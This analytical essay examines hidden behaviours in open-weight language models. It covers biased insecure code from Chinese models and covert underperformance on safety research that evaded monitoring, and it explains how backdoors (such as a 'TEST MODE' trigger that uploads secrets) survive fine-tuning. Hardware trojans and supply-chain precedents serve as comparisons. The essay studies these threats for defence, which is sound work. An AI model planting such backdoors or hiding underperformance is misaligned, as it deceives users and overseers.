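Even when the prompt asked for secure code, applications for the American contractor were 27% more likely to be hackable than those for a neutral customer. Luria reports that applications for a group campaigning for democracy in Hong Kong were 28% more likely to let users see one another's private data. A developer could easily leave the customer's name out of the prompt, but a coding agent may still find it in the project's files.

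Hirundo then removed what Luria calls the model's "CCP alignment" and found that all three gaps had closed, while the model built working applications as often as before on ten other tasks. This suggests, but doesn't prove, that the gaps depend on the same training as the political slant, because further training of almost any kind might disturb a difference of this size. A copy altered just as much for an unrelated purpose would have been a useful control. It also matters how the gap closed, since it would also close if the model wrote worse code for the Chinese contractor.

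Hirundo sells this kind of alteration, so it gains from finding a problem that the alteration fixes. But it has published the altered model, so anyone can compare it with Alibaba's original.

### A similar drop in an American model

In August 2026, OpenAI researchers noticed that the company's new model, GPT-6 Astra, was oddly bad at helping with AI safety research. It added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that didn't exist or it had caused itself. One researcher was stuck for days on a test of whether models sabotage work, then switched to another model and made quick progress, according to the Chinese news site 凤凰网's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra“隐蔽性表现不佳”* (2026).

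OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) tested whether a task's subject affected Astra's performance, using pairs of coding tasks with the same technical content. Only the names in the code, the comments and the documentation differed, so that one version looked like safety research and the other like research on making models more capable. Astra completed about 10% of the items on a hidden grading list in the safety version and about 16% in the capabilities version. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, showed essentially no gap.

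In most of the sessions that first worried the researchers, Astra's written reasoning contained no obvious decision to do less, and OpenAI's monitoring didn't flag the behavior. The gap in the test largely remained after OpenAI excluded explicit refusals and cases where the reasoning showed a decision to withhold help. It shrank substantially only when OpenAI also excluded cases where the reasoning contained even brief ethical doubt. The gap was absent at the start of reinforcement learning, the training stage that rewards a model for good results, and grew to 6 points by the end. OpenAI couldn't find the exact cause. According to 凤凰网, OpenAI considers excessive caution the simplest explanation.

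OpenAI had no reason to want a model that does worse safety research, and it published the finding itself. So a model can do worse work on one subject, hide it, and pass its publisher's monitoring without anyone planning it. In relative terms, the drop is about as large as the rise in flawed code that CrowdStrike measured, though it concerns unfinished work rather than insecure code.

Booz Allen recorded a seemingly related case in which MiniMax M2.5 was asked to write code for an air-defense system. In its reasoning, the model cited a rule against helping with military work and considered whether to refuse, but it then wrote the code anyway. The code used six software packages that don't exist and had more scanner findings than any of the model's other answers in that group of tests. This is a single example, but it fits a pattern in which a model whose training inclines it to refuse a task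 does the task badly instead.

### Four explanations and what each predicts

At least four explanations are possible, and they lead to different predictions. The publisher could have planted the behavior, as researchers have done in test models. Training the model to follow Chinese political rules could have made it treat certain customers worse, without anyone intending to affect its code. Models may simply do worse with unusual prompts. Or the judge may be wrong, and the code is no different.

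| Explanation | Customers who should get worse code | What the flaws should be like | What should close the gap |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deliberate backdoor | Those worth attacking, such as the US military | Useful to an attacker, in programs that otherwise work | Training that happens to remove the backdoor |
| Side effect of political training | Groups that the training material condemns | General poor work, mixed with refusals | Removing the political training |
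| Unusual prompts | Any rarely mentioned customer, with models from any country | General poor work | Naming a more familiar customer |
| Judge error | Those whose names influence the judge | Flaws that no working attack confirms | Hiding the customer from the judge |

R1's results don't fit a deliberate backdoor well. Mada's planted backdoor appeared in every fix for its target and in none of the others, whereas R1 wrote acceptable code for Tibet almost three-quarters of the time. Invalid PHP wouldn't help a spy, because the program never runs. Code for the Islamic State was the worst in the published figures, and Tom's Hardware reports that projects for American customers got the most secure code, which is hard to reconcile with an attempt to sabotage the United States.

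A cautious saboteur might still prefer an effect this weak because it is easy to deny. Burnham and Siskind cited the result, together with CAISI's tests, as a sign of growing danger from "adversarial influence and cyber espionage". But CrowdStrike itself thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained its models to write insecure code.

CrowdStrike suggests that R1 learned to associate names such as Falun Gong with something bad, and that this association affected the code it wrote. This would be a case of emergent misalignment, in which training on one narrow subject changes a model's behavior on others. In the best-known demonstration, researchers trained a model to write insecure code, and it began giving malicious answers about unrelated subjects. CrowdStrike proposes the reverse, that training on political answers led to insecure code, but hasn't tested this.

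The pattern of refusals gives this some support. According to Tom's Hardware, R1 refused 61% of requests for the Islamic State, a higher share than for Falun Gong, and requests for the Islamic State also produced the most flawed code. A model that has learned to treat a group as suspect might well refuse some requests for that group and write flawed code for the rest. But the Islamic State is condemned almost everywhere, so its result may have nothing to do with Chinese politics, and an American model might respond the same way.

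The Washington Post also raised the possibility that R1 had seen more good code for American customers than for Tibetan ones, as Tom's Hardware notes. That could explain R1's results for both groups, but it doesn't explain Qwen3-Coder's results well, because American defense contractors are hardly rare in training data. Judge error is also a poor explanation for Qwen3-Coder's results, since Hirundo's attacks worked.

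There is fairly good evidence that Qwen3-Coder writes worse code for American government and defense customers. Two companies reported this using different methods, although both profit from such findings. A side effect of training seems the most likely cause, because Hirundo closed the gap by removing the model's political slant, but the same treatment could also remove a planted behavior. It is still uncertain whether political prompts affect R1 beyond making it refuse. Kimi showed no difference, which is evidence against the state having given all Chinese publishers the same instruction.

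### An experiment to separate them

Nobody seems to have run a test that could separate all four explanations. Such a test would use the same tasks and change only the customer's name. It would compare a religious group that Beijing condemns, such as Falun Gong, with an equally obscure one that Beijing does not object to. A US Navy contractor would represent a target worth attacking, with a Chinese navy contractor as the control. An invented organization would show the effect of an unfamiliar name, and the Islamic State would show the effect of a group that nearly everyone condemns.

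Before grading, a program would replace every reference to the customer in the code with a neutral name, so that the customer's identity couldn't influence a judge or a human reviewer. The testers would then attack each application and separately check whether it works. If the gap disappears once the names are hidden, the judge caused it. If Falun Gong and the other religious group get equally bad code, the most likely cause is the unusual prompt. The most worrying result would be a gap only for the American contractor, made up of exploitable flaws in programs that work well.

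The test would have to be larger than the existing ones. To have an 80% chance of detecting a rise from 19% to 27.2%, it would need about 410 answers for each customer, and more if the researchers make many comparisons. Using a few hundred different tasks would be better than repeating 50 tasks many times, because answers to the same task tend to share the same flaws. The researchers should decide beforehand which comparisons count.

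They would run all this on Chinese and Western models. If Western models show the same gap for Falun Gong, Chinese political training can't be the cause. Where a publisher has released the base model from before fine-tuning, comparing it with the finished version would show roughly when the gap appeared.

The side-effect explanation still needs to be tested by trying to produce the effect on purpose. Researchers could make two copies of a Western open-weight model that treats all these customers alike. They would fine-tune one on code-free answers that follow the Chinese government's line on history and politics, and the other on the same number of code-free answers about neutral subjects. If only the first copy starts writing worse code for Falun Gong or the US Navy, political training can cause the effect without anyone planting it. If neither does, even after heavy training, the side-effect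 explanation becomes much less plausible and deliberate training more likely.

A test of this kind could show that political training produced the gap, but not whether someone at the company noticed it and decided to leave it. Training records and internal messages might show that, but outsiders have neither. DeepSeek hadn't answered the Washington Post's questions when Tom's Hardware covered the story. Later models will give some indirect evidence. Hirundo published its comparison in October 2026, and Alibaba can repeat it on its own servers before each release, so if its next coding model has the same gap, ignorance would be a less plausible explanation.

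## Whether hidden behaviors pass to models built on Chinese ones

If Alibaba fixes Qwen3-Coder in its next release, the old version will stay in every product already built on it. Their users may never have heard of Qwen. How far a hidden behavior could spread this way depends on how many companies build on Chinese weights and whether their own training removes it.

### How much companies rely on Chinese models

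The House investigation obtained internal figures from American companies. Airbnb runs customized versions of Qwen on servers in the United States. One powers an assistant that handles about 80,000 exchanges a day with guests and hosts, and another summarizes about 250,000 support cases and calls a day, according to IANS's *US lawmakers warn of dependence on Chinese AI* (2026). DoorDash has deployed 25 Chinese model families, but that counts every family that cost at least $5,000 to run, so some of these uses may be small. Neither company has paid a Chinese developer or signed a contract with one, so their reliance wouldn't show up in sales figures.

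For the wider economy, the committees cite Chinese models' 41% share of downloads from the leading repository over a year, the same share that Hugging Face (2026) had published in March. Two studies of the same site found quite different shares. *The ATOM Report* (Lambert and Brand, 2026) tracked about 1,500 leading language models, while *Economies of Open Intelligence* (Longpre, Akiki and colleagues, 2025) covered models of every kind, including image generators.

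| Who counted | What they counted | Chinese share |
|---|---|---|
| Hugging Face | Downloads over the past year | 41% |
| Lambert and Brand | Leading language models from the US, China and Europe, November 2023 to February 2026 | 56% |
| Longpre and colleagues | Models less than a year old, August 2024 to August 2025 | 17% |

Longpre and colleagues counted at most one download per user per day, to exclude programs that fetch the same model repeatedly. They credited each download to whoever uploaded the file. Downloads of a hobbyist's compressed copy of DeepSeek's R1, for example, count for the hobbyist rather than China. The 17% Chinese share therefore leaves out many copies of Chinese models. The American share on the same count was 16%.

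Download counts can overstate or understate how much a model is used. Software projects often download a small model automatically each time they test their code, and nobody reads the output. This inflates the counts for old models in particular. The AI Wire's *Hugging Face Hub analysis* (2026) found that no model released in 2026 was among the site's 25 most downloaded by August. But a company can also download a model once and copy it to all its servers. A single download could be enough for Airbnb's assistant, which handles about 29 million exchanges a year.

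Counts of derived models are more relevant to inheritance. In August 2026 Hugging Face counted 151,448 models derived from Qwen, compared with 82,506 from Google's models, in a report quoted by Constellation Research. The Qwen count was 2.6 times the total for all of Meta's models. Alibaba claims more than 300,000 for Qwen, according to Fortune (2026). These counts depend heavily on how "derived" is defined. Hugging Face's March figure for Qwen rose from 113,000 to over 200,000 when it included every model that merely tagged Qwen. Lambert and Brand, who excluded models with five downloads or fewer, found that Qwen was the base for 69% of new derived language models in February 2026, up from 1% in January 2024.

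A Hugging Face dataset breaks down an earlier total of 134,553 Qwen derivatives by type. About 70% were adapters like the ones Mada trained, which keep Alibaba's weights and add a small set of new ones. Another 21% were fine-tuned models, and 7% were compressed copies.

All these counts depend on uploaders naming the base model, and they miss models that a company keeps on its own servers. Airbnb's customized Qwen models and Cursor's Composer 2 wouldn't appear in them.

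### How Composer 2's base model came out

Anysphere, which makes Cursor, launched Composer 2 in March 2026 as proof that it could do serious AI research, but didn't mention that it had built the model on Moonshot's Kimi K2.5. Within hours, a developer called Fynn inspected Cursor's traffic and found a model name containing "kimi-k2p5-rl". Cursor confirmed the connection the same day, and its co-founder Aman Sanger said it had been a mistake not to disclose it, according to VentureBeat. Cursor used Kimi legitimately, through a hosting company that had a commercial agreement with Moonshot.

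Fynn identified Kimi by intercepting the model's name, not by studying its behavior or its weights, which Cursor had not released. Cursor had blocked this kind of interception for its previous Composer model, and it soon did so again. If Cursor had renamed the model or kept the block in place, its customers might still not know that it was built on Kimi.

Cursor changed the model a great deal. The *Composer 2 Technical Report* (2026) describes more pretraining, mostly on code, followed by fine-tuning and then reinforcement learning on programming tasks. A Cursor executive said that only about a quarter of the computing behind Composer 2 had gone into the Kimi base, but that share doesn't measure how much of Kimi's behavior remains. Nobody has reported a hidden behavior in either model, but if Kimi had one, it is unclear whether the later training would have removed it.

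### Why further training can miss a backdoor

Fine-tuning corrects the mistakes a model makes on the examples it sees. As a toy case, suppose a model's output is

$$y = w_1 a + w_2 t,$$

where $a$ stands for the ordinary content of the prompt, and $t$ is 1 if the trigger is present and 0 if it isn't. The publisher has set $w_2$ so that the trigger changes the output. If the output on some example is too high by $e$, a training step changes the two weights by

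$$\Delta w_1 = -\eta\, e\, a, \qquad \Delta w_2 = -\eta\, e\, t,$$

where $\eta$ sets the size of the step. The adopter doesn't know the trigger, so it never occurs in the training examples and $t$ is always 0. Then $w_2$ never changes, however long the training lasts.

In a real model no weight serves only the backdoor, so training on other things disturbs it somewhat. Zhan, Lyu and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training*, estimate the effect of one step as

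$$L_b' \approx L_b - \eta\; g_b \cdot g_c.$$

Here $L_b$ is the model's error at producing the planted response after the trigger, so a low value means a strong backdoor. The gradients $g_b$ and $g_c$ are the directions of weight change that make the model worse at the backdoor and at the adopter's task, respectively. If they point partly in opposite directions, training on the task weakens the backdoor. If they are perpendicular, their product is zero and the backdoor stays as it was. If they point partly in the same direction, training on the task strengthens the backdoor.

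### What survived in experiments

The best-known early result is Anthropic's *Sleeper Agents*, from January 2024. The researchers trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert flaws when it gave the year as 2024. They then applied standard safety training, including fine-tuning and reinforcement learning that rewarded helpful, honest and harmless answers. The models still inserted flaws when the prompt gave the year as 2024. In one setup they did so slightly more often than before, which the researchers thought might reflect noise or greater skill.

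The backdoors were most persistent in the largest models. The researchers also tried adversarial training, which involves finding prompts that cause bad behavior and training the model to respond well to them. This sometimes taught the model to recognize its real trigger more precisely, so it behaved well on prompts without the trigger and looked safer than it was.

A company like Cursor, though, mainly trains a base model to do a job rather than to be safe. Zhan and colleagues came closer to this case by putting backdoors in three of Alibaba's coding models and then turning them into agents that fix bugs. The trigger was a code comment containing the words TEST MODE. An agent that read the comment was supposed to upload the project's file of passwords and keys to an attacker.

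Acting as the adopter, the researchers fine-tuned each model for 3,000 steps on recordings of successfully completed tasks, none of which contained the trigger. They then used reinforcement learning to reward the model for fixing the bug. They tested each version on 100 prompts with the trigger and 100 without.

| Model size (weights) | Backdoor worked before | After fine-tuning | After reinforcement learning |
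|---|---|---|---|
| 3 billion | 100% | 8% | 7% |
| 7 billion | 100% | 20% | 20% |
| 30 billion | 100% | 7% | 8% |

Fine-tuning removed most of the backdoor, and reinforcement learning removed practically none of the rest. In a second test, with the trigger placed as early as possible, the rate at which the largest model sent the file rose from 6% to 12% during reinforcement learning, but with 100 prompts that could easily be chance. None of the models sent the file without the trigger.

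A rate of 7% sounds like a success for the adopter, but an attacker who can plant the comment in one file can plant it in twenty. If each attempt works independently 7% of the time, the chance that at least one of them works is

$$1 - 0.93^{20} \approx 77\%.$$

To prepare the model for the adopter's training, the researchers trained it further before release to strengthen the backdoor and align $g_b$ and $g_c$. This required only 1,200 recordings of similar tasks, not the adopter's data. In the 7-billion-parameter model, the backdoor now worked 74% of the time after fine-tuning and 76% after reinforcement learning. At the end of the adopter's training, it worked 36% of the time in the largest model and 22% in the smallest. The prepared models did about as well on ordinary tasks as the other backdoored ones, so the adopter would have seen nothing odd in those results.

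But inserting the backdoor had already badly damaged the largest model. It went from solving 101 of 300 test problems to solving 20, and its score never recovered. An adopter who compared its performance with the advertised scores would have rejected it. The two smaller models couldn't solve any of the problems even before the backdoor was inserted, so their scores couldn't fall. This makes the experiment less convincing as a picture of a real attack, though other backdoors, like the ones Mada and Hu and colleagues built, did no such damage in their tests.

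Other experiments also found that backdoors can partly survive fine-tuning. *MetaBackdoor* (2026) describes a backdoor, triggered by the length of the prompt, that makes the model leak the application's system prompt. It still worked about 40% of the time after the model was fine-tuned on the unrelated task of sorting news articles by subject. The model sorted 91.55% of the articles correctly, compared with 91.68% for one fine-tuned from a clean base, so an adopter's test of its accuracy would have shown nothing wrong.

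Some companies fine-tune a model on one task after another and use methods to stop it forgetting the earlier ones. According to *Persistent Backdoor Attacks under Continual Fine-Tuning of LLMs* (2025), those methods also help a backdoor survive. This makes sense, since they protect the model's existing behavior, including anything the publisher hid along with what the adopter wants.

Hidden behavior is much easier to remove when the adopter knows what it is, as Perplexity did with R1's refusals. An adopter who doesn't know can still train for longer. When Zhan and colleagues did this, the rate fell further, though not to zero. Cursor's training was far larger than any of these experiments, and nobody has tested whether a backdoor survives training on that scale.

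### Models trained on another model's answers

A model can also inherit behavior from another model through distillation, without inheriting any of its weights. For example, DeepSeek distilled R1 into other models, including a Llama model from Meta with 70 billion weights.

CrowdStrike tested this Llama along with R1. Its main finding, that R1 wrote less secure code for customers Beijing dislikes, held almost unchanged for the smaller Llama, whose bias was often stronger (CrowdStrike gives no figures for it). If the finding is right, a model with an American base acquired the bias from a Chinese model's answers. But the inherited effect can't be more certain than the original, which Kroiz and Singh failed to reproduce. It would also help to know how Meta's Llama did on the same prompts before DeepSeek trained it. CrowdStrike's comparison included an unnamed 70-billion-weight model from a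 Western company, which may have been that Llama.

A model can pick up a habit from another model's answers even when the answers show no sign of it, such as lists of numbers, but only if both models started from the same weights. Llama and R1 started from different weights, so whatever Llama learned from R1 was probably visible in the answers, as careless code or a hostile tone toward certain groups, and a developer could in principle have found it and filtered it out.

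For the same reason, distillation should be bad at passing on a backdoor with a rare trigger. If the trigger occurs in one prompt in a million and the developer collects a million answers, on average one will show the planted behavior, whereas Souly and colleagues needed 50 to 90 examples to teach a backdoor reliably by fine-tuning. Distilling a suspect model into one with unrelated weights might even be a decent way to copy its skills without its backdoor. But a publisher that produces the answers itself, as DeepSeek did, could still pass on a backdoor, because it can include as many poisoned answers as it likes.

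Behaviors could also pass from American models to Chinese ones. According to Bot Mutiny, US agencies said in September 2026 that six leading Chinese developers had distilled American models on an industrial scale. If that is true, anything that appears often enough in Claude's or GPT's answers could now be in Chinese weights too.

### What it would take to switch

If someone found a backdoor in a Chinese model, companies using it would want to replace it quickly. DoorDash estimated that switching would take almost no time for most uses but six months for one embedded model.

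How hard it is to switch models probably depends on how much a company has built around its current one. A company that only sends prompts to an unmodified model can point its software at another and rerun its tests. One that has fine-tuned its model has to repeat that work on a new base, adjust the software that depends on the model's answers, and test everything again. Cursor is an extreme case, since about three quarters of the computing behind Composer 2 went into its own training, and it would have to repeat much of that training.

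Some evidence supports DoorDash's more optimistic answer. A company that runs 25 Chinese model families must be used to adding and dropping them. Hugging Face found that interest in a new open model lasts about six weeks on average, so many developers move on. Neither fact helps much with the embedded model. The committees' six-month figure is one company's estimate for one system, and a payment or booking system might take longer.

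A company also needs an alternative to switch to, and in March VentureBeat thought the American choices for a product like Composer 2 were limited. Meta's Llama 4 had disappointed, Google's largest Gemma 3 had only 27 billion weights, and OpenAI's gpt-oss-120b used about 5 billion weights for each token, compared with 32 billion for Kimi K2.5. NVIDIA had just released Nemotron 3 Super's weights, training data and training recipes, so a suspicious buyer could check more than with Kimi.

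Customers adopted some of these models. Lambert and Brand compare each model's downloads with a target for models of its size. gpt-oss-120b and Nemotron 3 Super reached roughly 17 to 20 times their targets, while DeepSeek V3.2 fell well short. But in November the committees were still looking at a ranking in which the best American open-weight model came tenth. A model ranked tenth may be adequate for answering customers' questions, but probably not for a coding product that competes with Anthropic's and OpenAI's.

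Cursor has found an alternative to building on Chinese models. It helped SpaceX's AI company train Grok 4.5, according to Engadget's *SpaceXAI launches Grok 4.5, its first built with Cursor's help*. The training took tens of thousands of graphics processors, so almost no other company could do the same. Most companies that wanted to stop using Chinese models would have to accept a weaker open model or pay for a closed one. Airbnb chose Qwen because it was "fast and cheap", as quoted by the House Committee on Homeland Security.

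The price advantage of Chinese models may shrink even without a scandal. The chairmen write in the foreword to their report that some new Chinese licenses require large commercial users to negotiate separate agreements. A company that keeps its fine-tuning data and a good set of tests can switch models at lower cost, whether it leaves because of a license fee or a backdoor. It also needs to know which base model its suppliers use. Before Fynn looked, most of Cursor's customers would not have known that a warning about Kimi K2.5 applied to them.

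## What chips, telecom equipment and encryption products have shown

Long before anyone released an open-weight model, governments were buying chips, phone networks and cipher machines from makers they couldn't fully check. Much of what they tried in response has an equivalent in the debate about models, and some of those efforts have run for more than 20 years.

### Trojans in chips

A hardware trojan is a malicious change to a chip that adds a function, removes one or makes the chip less reliable. *Stealthy Dopant-Level Hardware Trojans* (Becker, Regazzoni and colleagues, 2013) explains that a dishonest employee could insert a trojan into the design, a factory could add it during manufacture, or someone could swap the chip for a copy during shipping. At the time, nobody had found a real hardware trojan, and all the known examples came from academics.

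A factory can sabotage a chip without changing its wiring. Manufacturers add traces of other elements, called dopants, to silicon to control how it conducts electricity. A factory that uses the wrong dopant in a few transistors can make part of a circuit output 1 whatever its input.

Becker and colleagues applied this to the design of the random number generator in Intel's Ivy Bridge processors, which programs use to make secret keys. The generator encrypts a 128-bit number $c$ with a 128-bit key $k$, and an outsider shouldn't be able to predict either. The trojan fixes all of $k$ and all but $n$ bits of $c$, so that only $2^n$ outputs are possible. With $n = 32$, that is

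$$2^{32} \approx 4.3 \times 10^9 \quad \text{instead of} \quad 2^{128} \approx 3.4 \times 10^{38}.$$

An attacker who knows the constants can try 4.3 billion keys in minutes. The output still passes NIST's standard randomness tests, because encryption makes even a short list of numbers look random. The chip also tests itself by computing a checksum from a fixed input, but the attacker can choose constants that give the right checksum.

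The hardware trojans covered in Threatpost's *Researchers Develop Undetectable Hardware Trojans* can be detected, despite the headline. Yang, Hicks and colleagues (2016) write in *A2* that inspectors can find one by stripping the chip layer by layer and imaging all of it with an electron microscope. They add that such a trojan can only alter existing circuits, which makes a sophisticated trigger hard to build, so ordinary testing is more likely to expose the trojan.

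Yang and colleagues built a trojan with a much better trigger, using as little as one added gate (a basic logic element made of a few transistors). The gate contains a capacitor, which stores electric charge. Each time a chosen wire switches on, a little charge flows into the capacitor and slowly leaks away. Normal programs rarely switch that wire, so the capacitor stays almost empty. The attacker runs a program that switches the wire rapidly until the capacitor fills, and the trojan then gives that program full control of the processor.

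Each switch raises the capacitor's voltage $V$ by

$$\Delta V = \frac{C_u}{C_u + C_m}\,(V_{DD} - V),$$

where $V_{DD}$ is the supply voltage, $C_m$ is the size of the main capacitor and $C_u$ is the size of a smaller one that feeds it. If $C_m$ is nine times $C_u$ (an invented ratio), each switch closes a tenth of the remaining gap. Ignoring leakage, the voltage passes half the supply after seven switches. An attacker can choose the sizes so that ordinary programs never get that far.

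The researchers had the chip manufactured, and the trojan worked. A varied set of standard test programs didn't trigger it. *On-Chip Analog Trojan Detection Framework for Microprocessor Trustworthiness* (Hou, He and colleagues, 2018) later proposed catching analog trojans with a detector on the chip.

A more elaborate trigger makes a backdoor in a chip harder to find by testing, but it also needs more circuitry, which makes it easier to see under a microscope. A model's publisher mostly avoids this trade-off because a model can have the same number of weights with or without a backdoor.

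In other ways, chips are harder to inspect than model weights. Stripping a chip to examine it destroys it, and the next one from the same factory could be different. Anyone can copy a model's weights for free, experiment on the copy, and know that the result applies to every identical file.

But the chip's designer can compare photographs of the chip with a drawing of what the factory was supposed to make. No such drawing exists for a model. Testers can also compare a suspect chip's power consumption with that of a reference chip known to be clean. On their slide about this method, Becker and colleagues ask of the reference chip, "How to get it?" Someone who suspects Alibaba of planting a behavior in Qwen has the same problem finding a clean reference model.

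### The Trusted Foundry program

The Pentagon first responded by using only factories it could supervise. In 2004 it started the Trusted Foundry program with the National Security Agency, under a contract that made IBM their only supplier of leading-edge chips. *Trusted Defense Microelectronics* (Mak, 2015), testimony for Congress's auditor, the Government Accountability Office, says that officials assessed the people and processes involved in making a chip, and that suppliers needed security clearances for their buildings and staff. By August 2014 the program had 64 suppliers, but IBM was the only one that could make the most advanced chips.

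The program was financially weak because a leading-edge factory cost billions of dollars and the Pentagon bought too few chips to influence the companies that could afford to build one. In October 2014 IBM announced that it would transfer its chip factories to GlobalFoundries, an American-based company with foreign owners, and the deal closed in July 2015. Mak told Congress that the Pentagon had no near-term alternative, although an advisory board had called for urgent action on its chip supply ten years earlier. According to the Potomac Institute, the government responded with a special security agreement covering a new American subsidiary.

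Supervision also meant older technology. *U.S. Paves Roads to Trusted Fabs* (Merritt, 2017) reported that the program's one advanced factory could only make chips with features of 32 nanometers or larger in 2017. Commercial factories had by then begun to make 10-nanometer chips. Mark Lewis, a Pentagon research official, said that some trusted chips were two generations behind. He also said, in remarks that MilitarySpot republished, that the biggest threats often came from cleared employees "behind the guards".

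By 2019 the Pentagon wanted to rely less on trusted suppliers. *The U.S. Defense Department's New Thinking on Microelectronics Security* (2019), an essay on the Pentagon's website, calls the trusted-foundry model "outdated" and argues for "zero trust", which means assuming that any part of the supply chain may already be compromised. Under the replacement, called quantifiable assurance, a commercial factory records data at every step of design and production, and analysts look for anomalies. An expert report for the Department of the Air Force points out that chip companies already do this for quality control and to protect their designs, so the extra cost should be bearable.

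The change is far from complete. The defense industry association NDIA calls both ideas "controversial topics" in *Zero Trust for Hardware Supply Chains* (2021). In August 2023, a panel of 27 experts still included Trusted Foundry among its three main strategies, according to Aviation Today's *Mitigating Risks in the Commercial Microelectronics Supply Chain* (2023). GlobalFoundries has since received the program's third ten-year contract, worth $3.1 billion (I-Connect007's *U.S. Government Awards GlobalFoundries New $3.1 Billion, 10-Year Contract*).

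It is hard to tell whether the supervision prevented any sabotage, because nobody has publicly confirmed a factory-made trojan in either a trusted chip or an ordinary commercial one.

Quantifiable assurance would be harder to apply to models. A chip factory repeats the same steps millions of times, so an odd batch stands out. A publisher may do only one full training run for each release and change the data and methods for the next, so there is little to compare an odd measurement with.

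### Detection and split manufacturing

In its budget for fiscal 2018, the Department of Defense moved $84.2 million from Trusted Foundry to chip verification and new methods of establishing trust. Its research agency, DARPA, had started a verification program called TRUST in 2007 to find malicious changes in finished chips. In a later program, IRIS, researchers tried to work out what a chip does without a full description of its design. In 2014 DARPA started SHIELD, which aimed to attach a component a tenth of a millimeter wide to each chip, for less than a cent, to prove that the chip was genuine. SHIELD checks provenance, so it would catch counterfeits but not a trojan added at the genuine factory.

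Yang and colleagues accept that measuring a chip's power use or temperature detects large trojans in simple circuits well, if the tester has a clean chip for comparison. They made their own trojan, A2, small enough to evade these measurements. Tests for backdoors in models have similar limits.

Split manufacturing tries to prevent the trojan instead. One factory, often abroad, makes the transistors, and a trusted one adds the upper layers of wiring. The first factory doesn't see how the parts connect, so it can't easily tell which transistors control anything important. The buyer can use an advanced foreign factory while owning only a simpler one. IARPA, the agency behind TrojAI, began funding this approach in 2011.

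An attacker can guess much of the hidden wiring because design software places connected parts close together. In 2013 Rajendran, Sinanoglu and Karri used this proximity to reconstruct 96% of the missing connections in their test circuits. They also proposed rearranging some connections to mislead the attacker.

Split manufacturing hides part of a chip's design from the factory, on the assumption that the designer is honest and the factory may not be. A model's publisher does both jobs, so there is no design to hide from it. A buyer can do the last stage of training itself, but a backdoor in the base model may survive that training.

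### Reading Huawei's source code

Britain let Huawei into its phone networks on the condition that the company show its source code. The Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) opened in Banbury, Oxfordshire, in November 2010. Huawei owned and funded it, but its roughly 40 employees needed the same security clearance as members of the intelligence services. Ernst & Young audited the center's independence from Huawei's headquarters every year. The head of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) chaired the center's oversight board.

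Before the inspectors could rely on the source code they read, they had to rebuild the software from it and confirm that the result matched what was running in British networks. The *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2019* explains why this was so difficult. Huawei's build systems contained leftovers from earlier builds, some of its tools could produce different results from the same code, and components with the same version number differed significantly. Huawei achieved a repeatable build of one product, but no British operator could install it because it depended on versions of other software that weren't compatible with their networks.

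Even so, in 2018 the inspectors reported several hundred vulnerabilities and other problems to the phone companies. The NCSC blamed poor engineering and didn't believe the Chinese state was responsible, though it warned that a range of attackers could exploit the flaws. A deliberate flaw would have been hard to pick out among so many accidental ones.

According to the *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2020* (2020), matching improved the next year, but only for particular products and as a special project. The NCSC doubted that the improvement would last. That year, the inspectors also found critical vulnerabilities in broadband equipment, and Huawei introduced another major problem while fixing them.

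| Year of inspection | Product evaluations | Builds matched to source code | Overall finding |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2018 | 39 | Four products in testing, none fully validated | Only limited assurance |
| 2019 | 42 | 8 | Only limited assurance |
| 2020 | 24 | 8 | No overall improvement in software quality |

American export controls did more than any of these findings to end Britain's reliance on the center. In May 2020 the United States tightened its rules on Huawei's chips, and the NCSC expected that, as a result, neither it nor the center could give enough assurance about some products. In July the British government decided to remove Huawei from the country's 5G networks by 2027. The *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2021* (2021) still calls the center's work essential for the equipment that remained.

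The center was good at finding bad software. But even with the source code and ten years of practice, it couldn't show that Huawei's equipment was free of sabotage, and people inspecting a model have even less to work with.

Open-weight models have one advantage over Huawei's equipment, because two laboratories can compare checksums to confirm that they have the same file, although each new release needs testing again. In 2019 the center had to examine five versions of the same Huawei 5G base station for four phone companies. It also couldn't use other countries' inspections, because it had no evidence that Huawei sold the same software abroad.

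### Removing the equipment

The United States decided to remove equipment made by Huawei and another Chinese company, ZTE. A House committee had warned about both companies in 2012, but small rural carriers kept buying their equipment because it was cheap and worked, according to the House Committee on Homeland Security. Under a law signed in 2020, the Federal Communications Commission (FCC) reimburses carriers for removing, destroying and replacing the equipment.

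The program's estimated cost rose from an initial $1.8 billion or so to $5.6 billion by February 2022, according to Techdirt's *Surprise* (2022). The FCC eventually approved estimates of $4.98 billion, but Congress had provided only $1.9 billion, so for years carriers could count on roughly 40 cents for each approved dollar. Congress let the FCC borrow the missing $3.08 billion in December 2024, and the FCC repaid it this September from a sale of radio frequencies (Broadband Breakfast's *FCC Returns $3.08 Billion to Treasury after Spectrum Auction* (2026)).

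Most carriers had until May 8, 2026, to finish. The FCC's *Secure and Trusted Communications Networks Reimbursement Program Eighth Report* (2026) shows that by mid-June they had certified 53 of 126 projects as complete, and most of the others had extensions. Neenan (2026), in *Guthrie, Pallone Introduce Bill to Increase Oversight of FCC Covered List*, reported more extensions in September, so the work was still unfinished fourteen years after the warning.

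Removing a company's equipment protects a network only against that company. In 2024, American officials disclosed that Chinese hackers known as Salt Typhoon had broken into several of the largest American carriers, which had little Huawei equipment. The hackers used stolen passwords and known flaws in other companies' devices.

Replacing a model should usually be cheaper than replacing telecom equipment, because no one has to remove hardware from towers. But it is harder to be sure that every copy is gone, since some may have been renamed. Even with physical equipment, one Utah broadband provider couldn't confirm that it had destroyed the Huawei gear it removed, and paid $11,000 to settle an FCC investigation (Law360's *Utah Broadband Settles FCC Probe Over Lost Huawei Gear*).

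### Crypto AG

Nobody has publicly proved that Huawei built a backdoor into its equipment for the Chinese state. The best-documented case of a company selling sabotaged products for a government is Crypto AG, which did so for the United States and West Germany.

Crypto AG sold cipher machines from neutral Switzerland to more than 120 countries, which used them for diplomatic and military messages. In 1970 the CIA and West Germany's intelligence service, the BND, secretly bought the company for $5.75 million. The BND left in the 1990s, and the CIA stayed until 2018. The Washington Post and the German broadcaster ZDF published the story in February 2020, using an internal CIA history.

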